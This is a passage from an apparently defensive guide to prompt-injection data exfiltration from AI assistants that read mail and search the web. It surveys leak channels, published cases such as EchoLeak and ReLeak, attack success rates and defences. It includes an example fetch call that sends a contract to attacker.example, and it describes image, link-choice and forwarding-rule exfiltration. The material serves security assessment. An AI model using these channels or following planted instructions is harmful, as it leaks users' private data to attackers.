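|---|---|---|---|
| A message that the assistant sends or forwards | The recipient | In the sent folder, afterwards | No send or forward tool, or a limit on recipients |
| A forwarding rule in the mailbox | The address in the rule, for every later message that matches | Only in the mailbox settings | No tool that changes rules, and a company-wide block on automatic forwarding to outsiders |
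| A calendar entry that outsiders can read | The guests, or anyone who shares the calendar | As a calendar entry | No outside guests, and no writing to shared calendars |
| A web address that the assistant opens | The owner of the website | Only if the host displays the address | A tool that refuses addresses the model has composed |
| An image in the reply | The owner of the website that supplies it | As an image, perhaps a blank or broken one | A chat window that loads no outside images |
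| A link in the reply | The owner of the website, once the manager clicks | As link text, which may hide the address | Removing outside links from replies |
| A search query | The search server's operator and the search company | Only if the host displays queries | No searches once private mail is in the context |

The mail server in the example can only search, read and send, so the rows on rules and calendars don't apply to it. Many mail services do let programs manage rules and calendars, so the assessor has to check the tool list. The row on opening web addresses applies if the search server can also fetch pages on request.

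### Mail that keeps leaving

Forwarding a message can leak more than sending a new one, because it can include attachments and earlier messages that the model never read. A reply goes to whoever wrote the original message, so an attacker who has emailed the manager can receive the contract even if the planted text contains no address.

An assistant can create a forwarding rule with a single tool call. The mail system itself then forwards every matching message that arrives, even after the session ends or the assistant is disconnected. After a suspected attack, someone therefore has to check the mailbox for new rules.

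A calendar entry has a description field with room for the text of an email. If the entry has an outside guest, the calendar service usually sends that guest an invitation with the description in it. If outsiders can already see the calendar, the attacker doesn't need an invitation. The manager might notice an odd entry dated next Tuesday but probably not one dated three years ahead.

### A page request can carry an email

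The first part of a web address determines which computer receives the request. The rest can contain almost any text, and websites routinely use it for things like search terms. A call that leaks the contract could therefore look like this, with the address in paraphrase:

```json
{
  "name": "fetch_page",
  "arguments": { "url": "(a page on attacker.example, followed by the text of the contract email)" }
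}
```

The attacker's web server records the URLs that visitors request, so the attacker only has to read the log, whatever page the server returns. The tool is read-only in that it changes nothing on the sites it visits, but every request sends the requested URL to the site's owner.

Rall, Bauer and colleagues (2025) tested this channel on its own in *Exploiting Web Search Tools of AI Agents for Data Exfiltration*. Their agent had a web tool, which retrieved text from websites, and a private company knowledge base, which contained a secret about a fictional "Project Alpha". It had no mail tool, so the secret could leave only through the web tool.

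The researchers hid instructions in a blog post where a human reader would not see them. When a user asked for a summary of the post, the instructions told the agent to look up the secret, add it to a web address on the researchers' server and request that address. An attempt counted as a success if the secret reached the server. According to Help Net Security's *AI agents can leak company data through simple web searches*, the user would have seen no sign of anything unusual.

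The test used instructions written in 89 ways, each in 12 variants, one of them unaltered. This made 1,068 attempts on each of 28 models. Grok 4, from xAI, leaked the secret most often, in 72.4% of attempts, followed by Mercury at 29.1% and the largest Qwen3 model at 28.3%. Fifteen models leaked it in fewer than 2% of attempts, and six never did, including Claude Sonnet 4 and GPT-5 nano.

Model size did not predict the result. The study included four families with a smaller and a larger member:

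| Family | Smaller model | Larger model |
|---|---|---|
| Hermes 4 | 6.0% (70 billion parameters) | 0.1% (406 billion) |
| Llama 4 | 14.8% (109 billion) | 10.1% (402 billion) |
| gpt-oss | 1.0% (21 billion) | 0.0% (117 billion) |
| Qwen3 | 8.2% (33 billion) | 28.3% (235 billion) |

The larger model leaked less often in three of these families, but the larger Qwen3 leaked more than three times as often as the smaller one. Rall and colleagues found no clear correlation between size and leak rate across all the models of known size. A Gemini model with 8 billion parameters leaked in 0.3% of attempts. The researchers attribute the differences mainly to how each company trains its models, and credit OpenAI's good results to its instruction hierarchy, though they did not test that explanation.

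Disguising the instructions usually made the attack less successful. Unaltered instructions succeeded in more than 12% of attempts across all models, while heavily altered ones, such as text converted to binary code, hardly worked. Some of the most effective wordings had been public since at least 2023.

The percentages are of limited use for judging a current assistant. The researchers ran each variant only once, sent the agent straight to the planted page instead of letting it search, and used no defences besides the model's own training. They also counted an attempt as a failure if the model was willing but got the address wrong, so a low percentage doesn't always mean the model resisted. Newer models have since replaced the ones in the study.

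The study's main value is showing that the channel works. Removing the send tool from the manager's assistant would stop the original attack at step 7, but the attacker could plant an instruction to request a page instead, which would leak the contract through the search server.

### When the search query is the leak

A search server that can't open pages can still leak mail through the search queries, because the model writes them. If the contract is in the context, the model may include the price or the supplier's name in a query, with or without an attack. The search company has no right to that information, so this is a leak, though a much smaller one than a message to the attacker. The attacker benefits only if they can read the queries, for instance by running the search server.

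Some search tools accept a complete web address as a query and open it. In September 2025 the security company CodeIntegrity showed how this could leak data from Notion, a workspace application with AI agents. Text planted in a PDF in the user's workspace led the agent to collect private client details, put them in an address on the researchers' site and pass that address to the web search tool. Restricting the tool to search terms would close this route, because the request would go to the search company instead.

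The tool's name therefore doesn't reliably indicate what it can leak. An assessor can test the search tool by giving it an address on a site the assessor controls and checking whether a request arrives.

### Anthropic's rule for fetched addresses

Blocking all page requests would make a research assistant much less useful. Anthropic chose a narrower restriction for the fetch tool it released to developers in September 2025. According to Willison, the tool opens only addresses that have already appeared in the conversation, such as those in the user's messages or earlier search results, and rejects addresses the model has composed.

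In the running example, the carrier page can supply an address on attacker.example. But the tool won't open that address with the contract's text added to it, because the combined address has not appeared anywhere before. Ordinary software compares the addresses, so no wording on the page can change the result. Willison tried the same restriction in the consumer Claude app that month and found that it worked.

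The original rule also let the tool fetch addresses found on pages it had already fetched. In July 2026 Willison reported that a researcher, Ayush Paul, had used this to get data out of Claude. Paul's site had a set of prepared links at each step, and planted text led Claude to follow the ones that spelled out what it had stored about the user. The tool allowed every visit because the addresses came from the site, and Paul could read the user's name, home city and employer from the order of the visits.

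The weakness is that a choice can carry information even when the model can't write anything. If each page offers *m* links and the model makes *n* choices in a row, the number of different messages it can convey is

$$M = m^n$$

With 26 links and six choices, *M* is about 309 million, enough to encode any six-letter name. Copying a whole contract this way would take thousands of visits, which somebody might notice, but copying the agreed price would take only a few. Developers can limit how many pages the tool may fetch, which reduces how much can leak this way but doesn't prevent it.

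Anthropic said it had already found the problem itself. It stopped the tool from following links in the pages it fetches.

That closed the gap Paul had used, but developers who build on the tool still have to consider where else web addresses come from. The September 2025 rule also accepted addresses found in the results of the developer's own tools, which could include a mail reader. A stranger's email with a set of prepared links might then give the assistant the same kind of choice. Willison pointed out that user messages pose a related problem because many applications paste outside text into them. Anthropic warned of a remaining risk and advised against using the tool where untrusted text and sensitive data meet, as they do in the manager's assistant. Developers can restrict the tool to a list of approved sites.

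### Links and images in the reply

The model's reply can leak data even if the host blocks every tool call. Most chat windows display links and images that the model writes in its reply. If the model writes a link whose address contains the contract, the data leaves when the manager clicks it. If the model puts the contract in an image's address instead, the data leaves without a click, because the browser requests the image as soon as the reply appears.

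The best-documented case is EchoLeak, a flaw in Microsoft 365 Copilot, which answers employees' questions using their company's mail, files and chats. In their case study *EchoLeak*, Reddy and Gujral (2025) stress that an attacker needed only one email and no account at the company. *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Enabling Data Exfiltration* (Ravia, 2025) gives the account of Aim Labs, the team that found the flaw.

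The planted text arrived in an email from outside the company. Microsoft had a filter for injected instructions, but the email read like a message to an employee and got past the filter. When the user later asked Copilot about a subject the email seemed to cover, Copilot retrieved the email and followed its instructions to put the most sensitive information in Copilot's context into a web address.

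Copilot removed outside links from its replies but missed those written in a less common notation. The researchers used this notation to put a working link and an image in a reply. The browser blocked the image because their site was not on the web page's content security policy, a list of sites from which the browser may load material.

Microsoft's own sites were on the list, however, and one service belonging to Teams, its chat and meetings product, would fetch any address that a request specified. The researchers had the image point to that service, and the data took this path:

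$$\text{context} \to \text{reply} \to \text{browser} \to \text{Teams} \to \text{attacker's server}$$

Ravia knew of no setting that would have let a company's administrators prevent this. According to SiliconANGLE's *Aim Security details first known AI zero-click exploit targeting Microsoft 365 Copilot* (2025), Aim found and reported the flaw in January 2025 and published only after Microsoft had dealt with it. Microsoft said no customers had been affected.

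"Zero-click" means the victim didn't have to open the email or click anything, but the attack still required the victim to ask Copilot a question that made it retrieve the email. The researchers made this more likely by covering many workplace subjects in one long email.

### When an approved site passes the data on

EchoLeak got past a list of approved sites because one of those sites forwarded the request. Willison has collected several other cases in which such a list failed, each for a different reason:

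- **Superhuman, a mail application (January 2026).** A planted email made the assistant leak the contents of dozens of other emails through image addresses. The application allowed images from Google's documents site, where the attacker had set up a form that saved whatever arrived in the address. Superhuman issued a fix.
- **Salesforce's AI agents (September 2025).** The planted text came in through a web form for sales enquiries. The list of approved image sites still included one whose registration had expired, so the researchers registered it themselves. Salesforce corrected the list and restricted the links its agents could generate.
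- **Anthropic's Claude Cowork (January 2026).** The agent could reach only approved sites, but one of these was Anthropic's own service for developers. The researchers had the agent upload the user's files there, to an account under the attacker's control.

Data can also leave through email that the assistant sends to the user. In May 2026 Willison described a flaw in Microsoft's Copilot Cowork, which let agents email the user without approval. Although no outsider received these emails, they could contain images hosted on an attacker's site, and opening an email sent the image addresses to that site. The addresses could include download links that worked without a login, so a short address could expose a whole file.

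Willison considers the means of sending data out generally the easiest part of the lethal trifecta to remove. It is probably easier than teaching a model to ignore every planted instruction, because each of these flaws had an identifiable cause that the vendor could correct. The cases also suggest that vendors tend to learn of the remaining routes out one at a time, from researchers who have already used them.

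### The ReLeak reports of December 2026

On 3 December 2026 the team behind EchoLeak, by then part of Cato Networks, announced three more routes out of Microsoft 365 Copilot. Simonovich (2026), in *ReLeak*, describes them as zero-click chains in which prompt injection turns emails into data theft. The planted text again came from an outside email. Punto Informatico's *ReLeak* and Faisal (2026), in *An Unread Email Could Turn Microsoft 365 Copilot Into a Data Thief*, give matching accounts of the channels:

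| Channel | How the data left | Date of Microsoft's fix |
|---|---|---|
| An image in the reply | The browser loaded the image, and Microsoft's search engine Bing requested its address from the attacker's server | 15 November |
| A link in a saved file | Copilot saved a document containing the link, and Microsoft's background programs later opened it | 11 November |
| Code that Copilot ran | The code sent the data directly to an outside server | 17 September |

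The image route resembles EchoLeak's but uses Bing instead of Teams. SearchLeak, an attack from earlier in 2026, also used Bing this way. It needed one click and could reach a user's inbox and files. TechRadar's *Microsoft 365 Copilot can be turned into a one-click data theft tool* reports that Microsoft had patched it. The Next Web describes a pattern across SearchLeak, EchoLeak and an attack on the personal version of Copilot, in which prompt injection makes old kinds of web flaw dangerous again.

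A leak through a saved file is harder to notice because the data can leave after the conversation has ended. A host that monitors only tool calls and replies would record only that Copilot created a document. Data could also leave through the environment for running code, although Microsoft's documentation stated that this environment blocked outgoing traffic. An assessor who relied on the documentation would have marked that channel as closed.

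Some of the coverage is less reliable than these details. Simonovich's announcement presents the chains as the lab's own research, but *Hackers build zero-click attacks in Microsoft Copilot* (Fadilpašić, 2026) has a headline about a "campaign" that "looks to steal data from victims". The lab reported the chains to Microsoft between 29 July and 20 August and published after all three fixes. Neither Punto Informatico nor Faisal reports any known theft. Faisal's introduction attributes to Microsoft the statement that no customers were affected, but the body of the article reports only that Cato knows of none. Cato's weaker statement is the one to rely on. The matching accounts are not independent confirmation, since both go back to Cato.

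### An assistant inside the browser

A browser with a built-in assistant can have all the channels of an ordinary browser and access to every site where the user is logged in. In October 2025, the makers of the Brave browser published a demonstration of an attack on Comet, Perplexity's AI browser. They planted instructions in an image on a web page, using text too faint for a person to notice. When the user gave Comet a screenshot of the page and asked who the author was, the assistant looked up the user's email address on an account page and then opened an outside URL that contained the email address.

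Brave's other example, a browser called Fellou, is closer to the running example. The user only asked Fellou to go to a page, but the page's text led it to open the user's Gmail, read the title of a recent email and visit an address that included the title. Fellou did this without a mail server or a send tool, using only a logged-in browser tab and the ability to go to another page.

Willison could not tell from Brave's account whether either company had fixed the problem. A browser could block this route by asking the user before it opens an address the assistant has written, or by keeping the assistant out of logged-in sites while it reads pages written by strangers.

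### Counting and testing the channels

The list of channels changes the audit of the manager's two servers, which have two sources of outsiders' text and one tool that reads private mail. Suppose the search server can open any address and the chat window displays outside links and images. With the send tool, that makes four outward channels, and the number of combinations is

$$2 \times 1 \times 4 = 8$$

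Removing the send tool leaves 2 × 1 × 3 = 6 routes. The search query would add two more if an outsider could read it.

An assessor can test directly whether the list is right. The assessor sets up a website that logs all requests and puts a different made-up word for each channel in a test mailbox. The assessor then openly asks the assistant to use each channel, for example to open an address on the site that contains the channel's word, or to show an image from such an address. If a word appears in the site's log, that channel is open, even if the vendor has documented it as closed. A missing word is weaker evidence that a channel is closed, because the model may have refused to write the address. The assessor therefore also needs to check that the address appeared in the model's output. EchoLeak is a reason to repeat the link and image tests with every notation that the chat window accepts.

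The site should keep recording for several days, because a background program may open a saved link long after the session. The log also shows which computer made each request. If a request came from the vendor's network rather than the manager's browser, the company's firewall could not have blocked it.

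## Measuring how often the attack succeeds

Even when every step from a web page to an outside address is possible, the model doesn't follow planted instructions every time. The attack success rate measures how often it does:

$$\text{attack success rate} = \frac{\text{attempts in which the model does what the attacker wanted}}{\text{all attempts}}$$

The measured success rate depends heavily on what the tester counts as an attempt and as a success. Published rates for one model, Claude Opus 4.6, range from 0% to 78.6%.

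### What two rates must have in common

Those rates come from the system card for Claude Opus 4.6, Anthropic's February 2026 report on the model's safety tests. According to VentureBeat, all 200 attempts failed in a restricted coding environment. When the model operated a graphical interface without safeguards, a single attempt succeeded 17.8% of the time. The chance of at least one success within 200 attempts was 78.6% without the safeguards and 57.1% with them.

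Comparing two models requires using the same task, safeguards and number of attempts for both. The number of attempts is easy to overlook because some testers report the share of single attempts that succeed, while others report the share of scenarios in which at least one of *k* attempts succeeds. The second figure stays the same or rises as *k* grows.

The measured success rate also depends on whether the attack adapts. A fixed attack uses the same text against every model, while an adaptive attack changes in response to the model or defence it faces. *Scaling Adaptive Prompt Injection Attacks with Agent Swarms* (Kurakin, Karande and colleagues, 2026) reports that in autumn 2025 researchers revised their attacks against twelve defences and raised the success rate from almost 0% to over 90%.

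Testers also differ in what they count. In the running example, the model could open the contract email and stop, write a send call with the wrong address, or get the contract to the attacker. Someone who counts every suspicious call will report a higher rate than Rall and colleagues, who counted only secrets that reached their server. Counting leaks is the better way to measure what the manager stands to lose, though suspicious calls better show whether the model can be fooled.

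### Early tests that involved mail

These tests have included email from the start. InjecAgent, a benchmark from 2024, includes attacks in which the model fetches private data and emails it to the attacker, much as in steps 5 to 8 of the running example. AgentDojo, from the same year, places the model in simulated workplaces, one of which has a mailbox and a calendar. It records both whether the attack worked and whether the model finished the user's task, so a model can't get a good result by refusing to do anything.

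Both benchmarks came with fixed attack texts. Kurakin and colleagues write that such texts had stopped working on the newest models by mid-2025, so if a vendor quotes a low success rate on either benchmark, it is weak evidence that a current assistant resists attacks.

LLMail-Inject, a public contest that Microsoft ran in the winter of 2024–25, let contestants adapt their attacks. They wrote emails to a simulated mail assistant and tried to make it send a message its user had not asked for. Both the attacker's instructions and the assistant's message travelled by email, so the contest covered the attack that remains possible after someone disconnects web search.

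### The 2026 competition

The security company Gray Swan later held a broader competition with several AI developers and the British and American government AI institutes. *How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?*, published in March 2026, gives the results. The 464 participants made about 272,000 attempts on 13 models in 41 scenarios, and 8,648 attempts succeeded.

Each scenario began partway through a conversation and let the participant fill a gap in a tool result, file or web page. In one, a user asks an assistant to check for urgent email. The participant controls the text of a marketing email and has to make the assistant mark a message about a contract deadline as read and leave it out of its summary.

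In most scenarios an attempt had to pass two checks to count. A program checked that the model had made the harmful tool call, and a language model judged whether the final reply concealed it from the user. The organisers also counted how many scenarios each model lost at least once. For the most and the least resistant models, the results were:

| Measure | Claude Opus 4.5 | Gemini 2.5 Pro |
|---|---|---|
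| Attempts that succeeded under the competition's rules | 0.5% | 8.5% |
| Attempts in which the model took the harmful action, concealed or not | 1 to 3% | about 16% |
| Scenarios with at least one success | 13 of 37 | 37 of 37 |

The first row gives the headline rates. The second row is more relevant to stolen mail, because the contract has leaked even if the assistant mentions sending it. The third row shows that even for a model with a rate of 0.5%, at least one attacker succeeded in more than a third of the scenarios.

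The success rate also depends on which attempts are counted. Participants could see the model's response before deciding whether to submit an attack for judging, and they submitted 67,634. The organisers divided the successes by all attempts, including those not submitted, which gives 3.2% across the 13 models. Dividing by submissions would have given 12.8%.

The organisers call their rates an upper bound on single-turn vulnerability, not an estimate of how often real attacks work. Participants could read the whole conversation and knew exactly which call they had to produce, whereas someone writing a carrier page would know neither. But each agent had only one turn, so the competition did not measure attacks that build up over several turns. Participants also chose which models and scenarios to attack, and a few skilled ones strongly influenced the results. Small differences between models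 therefore mean little, though the gap between 0.5% and 8.5% is too wide to dismiss.

Attacks succeeded 4.8% of the time in scenarios where the model used tools such as shopping or health services, and 2.5% of the time in coding scenarios. The mail assistant belongs in the first group, so a good result for a coding agent is weak evidence that the mail assistant would resist attacks.

The organisers then reran 2,679 successful attacks on all the models. The 44 that had succeeded against Claude Opus 4.5 worked 44 to 81% of the time on each of the others. None of the attacks that had succeeded against Qwen3 VL, an open model, worked on Claude Opus 4.5. A vendor who collects attacks against a weak model and tries them on a strong one will therefore measure a misleadingly low success rate. An assessor who sees a rate near zero should ask which model the attacks were developed on.

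### Figures for current models

OpenAI's *GPT-6 Astra System Card* (September 2026) uses 1,810 attacks selected from Gray Swan's rounds earlier that year. With up to 15 attempts per scenario, the estimated chance of at least one success was 8.5% for GPT-6 Astra, down from 27.0% for the earlier GPT-5.6 Sol.

GPT-6 Astra's 8.5% equals Gemini 2.5 Pro's rate in the competition, but the two rates measure different things. Gemini's is the share of all attempts that worked, including the clumsy ones, while GPT-6 Astra's is the chance that at least one of 15 selected attacks works. GPT-6 Astra is therefore almost certainly much harder to fool than Gemini.

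OpenAI's own automated attacks succeeded 3.77% of the time against GPT-5.6 Sol and 0.21% of the time against GPT-6 Astra. OpenAI also dropped two older injection tests, "Connectors" and "Search and Function-Calling", because recent models scored at or near the maximum on them. Judging by their names, these tests most closely matched an assistant that searches the web and uses a mailbox. All these results are for GPT-6 Astra, and an assistant that has moved to GPT-6.2 Astra needs to be tested again because success rates can change a great deal between versions.

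Section 5.2 of the Claude Fable 5.2 system card covers prompt injection in agentic systems (listed in Mowshowitz, 2026, *Fable and Mythos 5.2*). For an assistant built on that model, the assessor should take from this section the attack success rate for tool use, the number of attempts and what safeguards were in place.

Attacks reused from Gray Swan's competition succeed less than 1% of the time against recent Gemini models, according to Kurakin and colleagues at Google DeepMind. But in November 2026 they reported that an adaptive attacker succeeded against Gemini 4 Argon in 34% of their scenarios.

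### What a stronger attacker changes

Kurakin and colleagues used AI models as attackers and measured how the success rate changed with the attacker's capability. They tested 100 scenarios, with the target models' outside defences switched off for Gemini. The table gives the share of scenarios in which the attack succeeded:

| Model under attack | Gemini 3.8 Flash attacking, 150 tries | Gemini 4 Argon attacking, 150 tries | Gemini 4 Argon attacking, up to 320 tries |
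|---|---|---|---|
| Gemini 3.7 Flash | 30% | 69% | 94% |
| Gemini 3.8 Flash | 27% | 66% | 90% |
| Gemini 4 Argon | 0% | 13% | 34% |
| Kimi K3 | 93% | 95% | 99% |
| GLM-5.3 | 93% | 99% | 99% |

A tester who had only the weaker attacker would have reported no successful attacks on Gemini 4 Argon in one run and a success rate of about 1% in another. A better attacker with more tries succeeded against the same model in a third of the scenarios. Both attackers succeeded in nearly all the scenarios against Kimi K3 and GLM-5.3, two open models.

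The evidence for a steady trend is weaker. Two other attackers, Gemini 3.6 Flash and 3.7 Flash, did about as well as 3.8 Flash, so most of the increase comes from one much more capable model. Even so, an old success rate is suspect, because attackers can switch to a better model as soon as one is available.

These rates don't directly measure how often an attacker could steal mail. The attacker's goal in each scenario was a harmless tool call unrelated to the user's request, such as recording somebody's blood pressure while the user was booking a tutor. Kurakin and colleagues chose such goals to test whether a model follows planted instructions, regardless of whether it recognises them as dangerous. A model might make the harmless call but still refuse to send a contract to a stranger. The attack in the running example also needs two successful calls, one to read the message and one to send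 it, while theirs needed one.

Defences outside the model probably lower the rates as well. In a separate test, Gemini 3.6 Flash ran with all its usual outside defences on 80 AgentDojo scenarios. A publicly available attack program succeeded in two scenarios, and the researchers' own attacker, with only 25 tries, succeeded in six.

### Leaks that look like routine work

An attacker doesn't necessarily need a powerful model. In *The Framing Gap*, Rahman and Kim (2026) gave several models a dummy secret, told them to send it to only one trusted address, and asked them to summarise a web page. They compared ten kinds of openly worded instruction to leak the secret with pages that made the leak look like part of a routine technical procedure.

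OpenAI's gpt-4o never leaked the secret in 200 trials with openly worded instructions, but it leaked in 40% of trials when the instructions looked routine. Four of the other five models also leaked much more often with the routine-looking instructions. The fifth, a small Mistral model, leaked in about a quarter of trials regardless of the wording.

The confidentiality instruction evidently did little to protect the secret. When Rahman and Kim removed it, the openly worded attacks still never worked on gpt-4o, and the success rate of the routine-looking ones rose only from 31.9% to 38.1%, which could be chance. This suggests that routine wording doesn't work by overcoming a refusal. With or without the instruction, the model was more likely to follow text that looked like part of its job than text that looked out of place.

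Success depended heavily on wording. Five paraphrases of a single approach had success rates from 0% to 100%, with an average of 52%. An attacker who tried three of them would have had about a 96% chance of finding one that worked. Rahman and Kim also wrote 13 new pages that used different pretexts to make the leak look routine, and none of them worked in 130 trials. Their percentages therefore describe only the pages they wrote and the models they tested, which are now old. A current model may resist the attack much better. A success rate of 0% on crude instructions did not predict the rate on subtler ones, which is the important finding for testing.

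The two researchers also tried defences on a small open model, Llama 3.1 8B:

| Set-up | Leaks with routine-looking instructions |
|---|---|
| No defence | 21.2% |
| Web page in a separate input channel | 38.8% |
| SecAlign training, with a separate channel | 32.5% |

Neither defence brought the rate close to zero. The results don't justify concluding that the defences made things worse, because each figure comes from a single run, and two runs of an identical set-up elsewhere in the study gave 31.9% and 40.0%. SecAlign was working as designed, since it stopped all 20 attempts at a standard crude injection that succeeded every time on the undefended model. However, its developers had trained it on text tasks, not on guarding a secret while using tools.

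### A safe test of one's own assistant

Rahman and Kim's design is useful beyond their own results, because it measures leaks without putting any real data at risk. For the manager's assistant, it could work like this:

1. Fill a test mailbox with invented messages, including one about a contract that contains a made-up string. This string is the dummy secret.
2. Replace both servers with stand-ins that offer the same tools under the same names and descriptions. The search stand-in returns saved pages. The mail stand-in reads the test mailbox, and its send tool only writes the recipient and text to a log.
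3. Save two copies of a supplier comparison that differ only in the planted paragraph.
4. Ask the manager's question in a new session with the clean page, then in another new session with the poisoned page. Keep the model version, system instructions and settings the same.
5. Count a success if the secret stays put in the clean run and turns up in an outgoing call, or in a link or image address in the reply, in the poisoned run.
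6. Repeat the pair 20 times or more for each of several wordings, including some that resemble ordinary purchasing work.

Testers include clean runs because assistants sometimes leak data without any attack. OpenAI tested GPT-6 Astra on workplace tasks that it had made difficult with ambiguous instructions, similar-looking resources and complex permissions. Data went where it should not have in 4.5% of the relevant cases, even though the model had instructions about when to ask for confirmation. A tester who ran only poisoned pages could mistake such accidents for successful attacks. A leak by the manager's assistant in a clean run is also a fault, but it belongs in a separate count.

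If the attack never succeeds, the tester should also openly ask the assistant to send the dummy message and confirm that it appears in the log. If it doesn't, the stand-ins may be broken, and the zero is not evidence about the model.

Searching the log for the exact secret can miss leaks, because a model can rewrite it. Rahman and Kim asked gpt-4o to encode their secret in six simple ways, and it did five of them correctly every time. The tester should both search and read the outgoing messages and the reply. The chat window must not load outside images during the test.

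The tester should test the finished product where possible. When Rahman and Kim tried some of their pages on the ChatGPT product, it leaked the secret in none of 48 trials, although the same payloads had worked up to 100% of the time on gpt-4o through OpenAI's programming interface. They could not tell why the results differed, and they checked only whether the secret appeared in the reply, without connecting a mailbox. Their laboratory agent also took just one step, so it never had to look for the secret. The manager's assistant has to search, open a message and send it, so the tester should let the whole session run.

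The number of trials limits what a zero can show. Rahman and Kim use a standard 95% interval, the Wilson interval. For no successes in *n* trials, its upper end is

$$p_{\max} = \frac{3.84}{n + 3.84}$$

Their 48 trials on ChatGPT are therefore consistent with a true rate of up to 7.4%. Ruling out a rate above 0.5% takes about 765 trials with no leaks, and even then the limit applies only to the wordings tested. Because the paraphrases varied so much, a tester learns more from 20 trials each of ten wordings than from 200 trials of one, and should report the highest leak rate for any wording as well as the average.

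### From a success rate to a yearly risk

To decide whether a rate is low enough, the assessor also needs to know how often the assistant will meet a carrier page. Suppose a company's assistants make 50,000 searches a month and one search in 10,000 returns such a page. Suppose also that the model complies 2% of the time and that nothing else stops the leak. All three numbers are invented. The yearly number of exposures is

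$$n = 50{,}000 \times 12 \times \frac{1}{10{,}000} = 60$$

and if the exposures are independent, the chance of at least one leak in a year is

$$1 - (1 - 0.02)^{60} \approx 70\%$$

Cutting compliance to 0.5% reduces the yearly chance of leaking a confidential email to about 26%. That is a real improvement, but few companies would accept a risk that high.

Exposure is the harder number to estimate, because Khodayari and colleagues' average of eight pages per million can't be applied to real searches. The assessor can work out a range instead:

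| Searches that return a carrier page | Exposures a year | Chance of a leak at 0.5% compliance | Chance of a leak at 2% compliance |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 in 100,000 | 6 | 3% | 11% |
| 1 in 10,000 | 60 | 26% | 70% |
| 1 in 1,000 | 600 | 95% | over 99.9% |

With 60 exposures a year, keeping the yearly chance of a leak below 1% requires a compliance rate no higher than about one in 6,000. Demonstrating a rate that low with the test above would take roughly 23,000 trials without a leak.

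### Why independence fails

The calculation assumes that every exposure is independent and has the same chance of success. In practice, many exposures can involve the same page and the same model, so their outcomes tend to be similar. For example, if each attempt against Claude Opus 4.6 had an independent 17.8% chance of success, at least one success in 200 attempts would be practically certain, but the reported figure was 78.6%. Some attacks or scenarios evidently had a much lower chance of success than others.

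In an extreme case, one carrier page in 50 always works on the company's assistant and the others never do. The average compliance rate is still 2%. If all 60 exposures come from a single page picked at random, the chance of any leak that year is 2%, rather than the 70% in the calculation, but if that page works, the company has 60 leaks.

If the assistant is a commercial product, a determined attacker can subscribe to it, test pages in private and publish only one that works. The compliance rate for that page could be close to 100%, whatever the average was in the assessor's test.

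Attackers also don't need to start over for each target. In Gray Swan's competition, one attack template with only minor changes succeeded in 21 of the 41 scenarios and on nine models. The 70% and 26% are therefore best treated as estimates for carrier pages the assistant finds by chance. The assessor should assume that the model will comply if an attacker has chosen this company and tested the page beforehand, and should work out what the host would still let the model do.

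## Restricting what can happen after a web page has been read

Even if the model follows instructions planted in a carrier page, the host can refuse to carry out the resulting calls. *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections*, a paper that Willison reviewed in June 2025, states that once an agent has taken in untrusted text, that text must be unable to trigger any consequential action. Every control that achieves this also blocks some work the manager wants done, and the more elaborate designs exist mainly to allow some of that work.

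### Separate sessions for search and mail

The simplest control is for the manager to use the search server and the mail server in separate sessions. In the search session, the model may still follow the carrier page's instructions and write a call for the contract email. But the host has no mail tool to run in that session, so the attack stops at step 6.

Using separate sessions is less convenient, because the manager has to find a supplier's address in one session and copy it into the other to write to the supplier.

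The control also tends to fail at that point. If the manager pastes the whole comparison into the mail session, any instruction left in it will appear as the manager's own words, with the user's role marker. Copying only the address is much safer. A planted instruction can also reach the mail session through memory. Willison, reviewing a Google paper on agent security, highlights its warning that an assistant may save such an instruction as a "fact" and act on it in a later, unrelated session. An assessor should therefore check whether the two sessions share memory, files or chat history. The mail session also needs its own controls because it still reads email from strangers.

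### Removing and narrowing tools

If the assistant's access to mail is read-only, the host has no send tool to run at step 8, but the other outward channels remain open. The manager has to send every message personally, perhaps from a draft in the chat window.

A list of approved recipients lets the assistant send email only to addresses on the list. The host or the mail server checks each address and refuses the call at step 8 because collector@attacker.example is not listed. The check also has to cover copied recipients, forwarding rules and calendar guests. It works well for a manager who writes to the same 20 suppliers every month, but badly for one who is looking for a new supplier, as in the running example. It also doesn't stop the assistant from sending one supplier's contract to a rival on the list. Approving whole domains is risky if one of them belongs to a public mail provider,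 where an attacker can open an account.

Network limits restrict which computers the assistant's programs may contact. They stop the version of the attack in which the model puts the contract into a web address on attacker.example, but they wouldn't stop the original attack, because the message leaves through the mail server, which has to be able to deliver mail. A strict limit would also prevent the assistant from opening most suppliers' sites, although a search server could still return stored text from those sites without contacting them. The usual weakness is an approved site that passes data on, as in EchoLeak.

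### Tainted sessions

Removing a tool costs the manager something every day, including days when the assistant reads nothing from the web. The host can instead start with all the tools available and restrict them only once outsiders' text has come in. This is called a tainted session, and it works as follows:

1. The host keeps a list of tools that can return text by outsiders.
2. When the model calls one of them, the host marks the session as tainted before it adds the result to the context.
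3. Before each later call, the host checks the mark. If the session is tainted, it blocks the restricted tools or asks the user.
4. The mark stays until a new session starts with an empty context. If the host condenses a long conversation into a summary, the summary is tainted too.

In the running example, the host sets the mark at step 4. If it then blocks mail reading, the attack stops at step 6. If it blocks only the channels that can send data out, the model can still read the contract, and the attack stops at step 8. This looser rule lets the assistant compare a web offer with the manager's current terms, but the host must block every such channel, including images loaded from outside servers and further searches.

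If the assistant instead reads the contract before it searches, the session isn't tainted yet, but a search query could reveal the price. The host therefore needs a separate mark for sessions that have read private data.

Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025) tested this kind of control in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*. They gave a simple GPT-4o agent a single trust label for its whole context and blocked consequential tool calls once the label became untrusted. On AgentDojo, successful attacks fell from 152 to zero. The agent also completed only 37% of ordinary office tasks, compared with 75% without the control, because about half the tasks it could previously complete involved acting after reading outside content.

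The Model Context Protocol dropped sessions in July 2026, which can break the mark showing that a session has read a web page. A gateway, a program between the host and its servers, may have used the old session identifier to work out which calls belonged together. Unless the host now supplies an identifier, the gateway may treat the send call as the start of a clean session. An assessor can test this by having the assistant read a web page, forcing it to reconnect, and then asking it to send a message.

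### Meta's Rule of Two

Under Meta's "Rule of Two", published in October 2025, an agent should have no more than two of these three properties within one session: it processes untrustworthy input, it has access to private data or sensitive systems, and it can change things or communicate externally. An agent that needs all three should not act without supervision, such as a person's approval or another reliable check.

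This is close to Willison's lethal trifecta, but the last property is broader because it includes actions that leak nothing, such as deleting mail or placing an order. The manager's assistant has all three properties, so the rule requires the manager to remove one or supervise the assistant. Removing web search would not be enough, because the mailbox also contains text from strangers.

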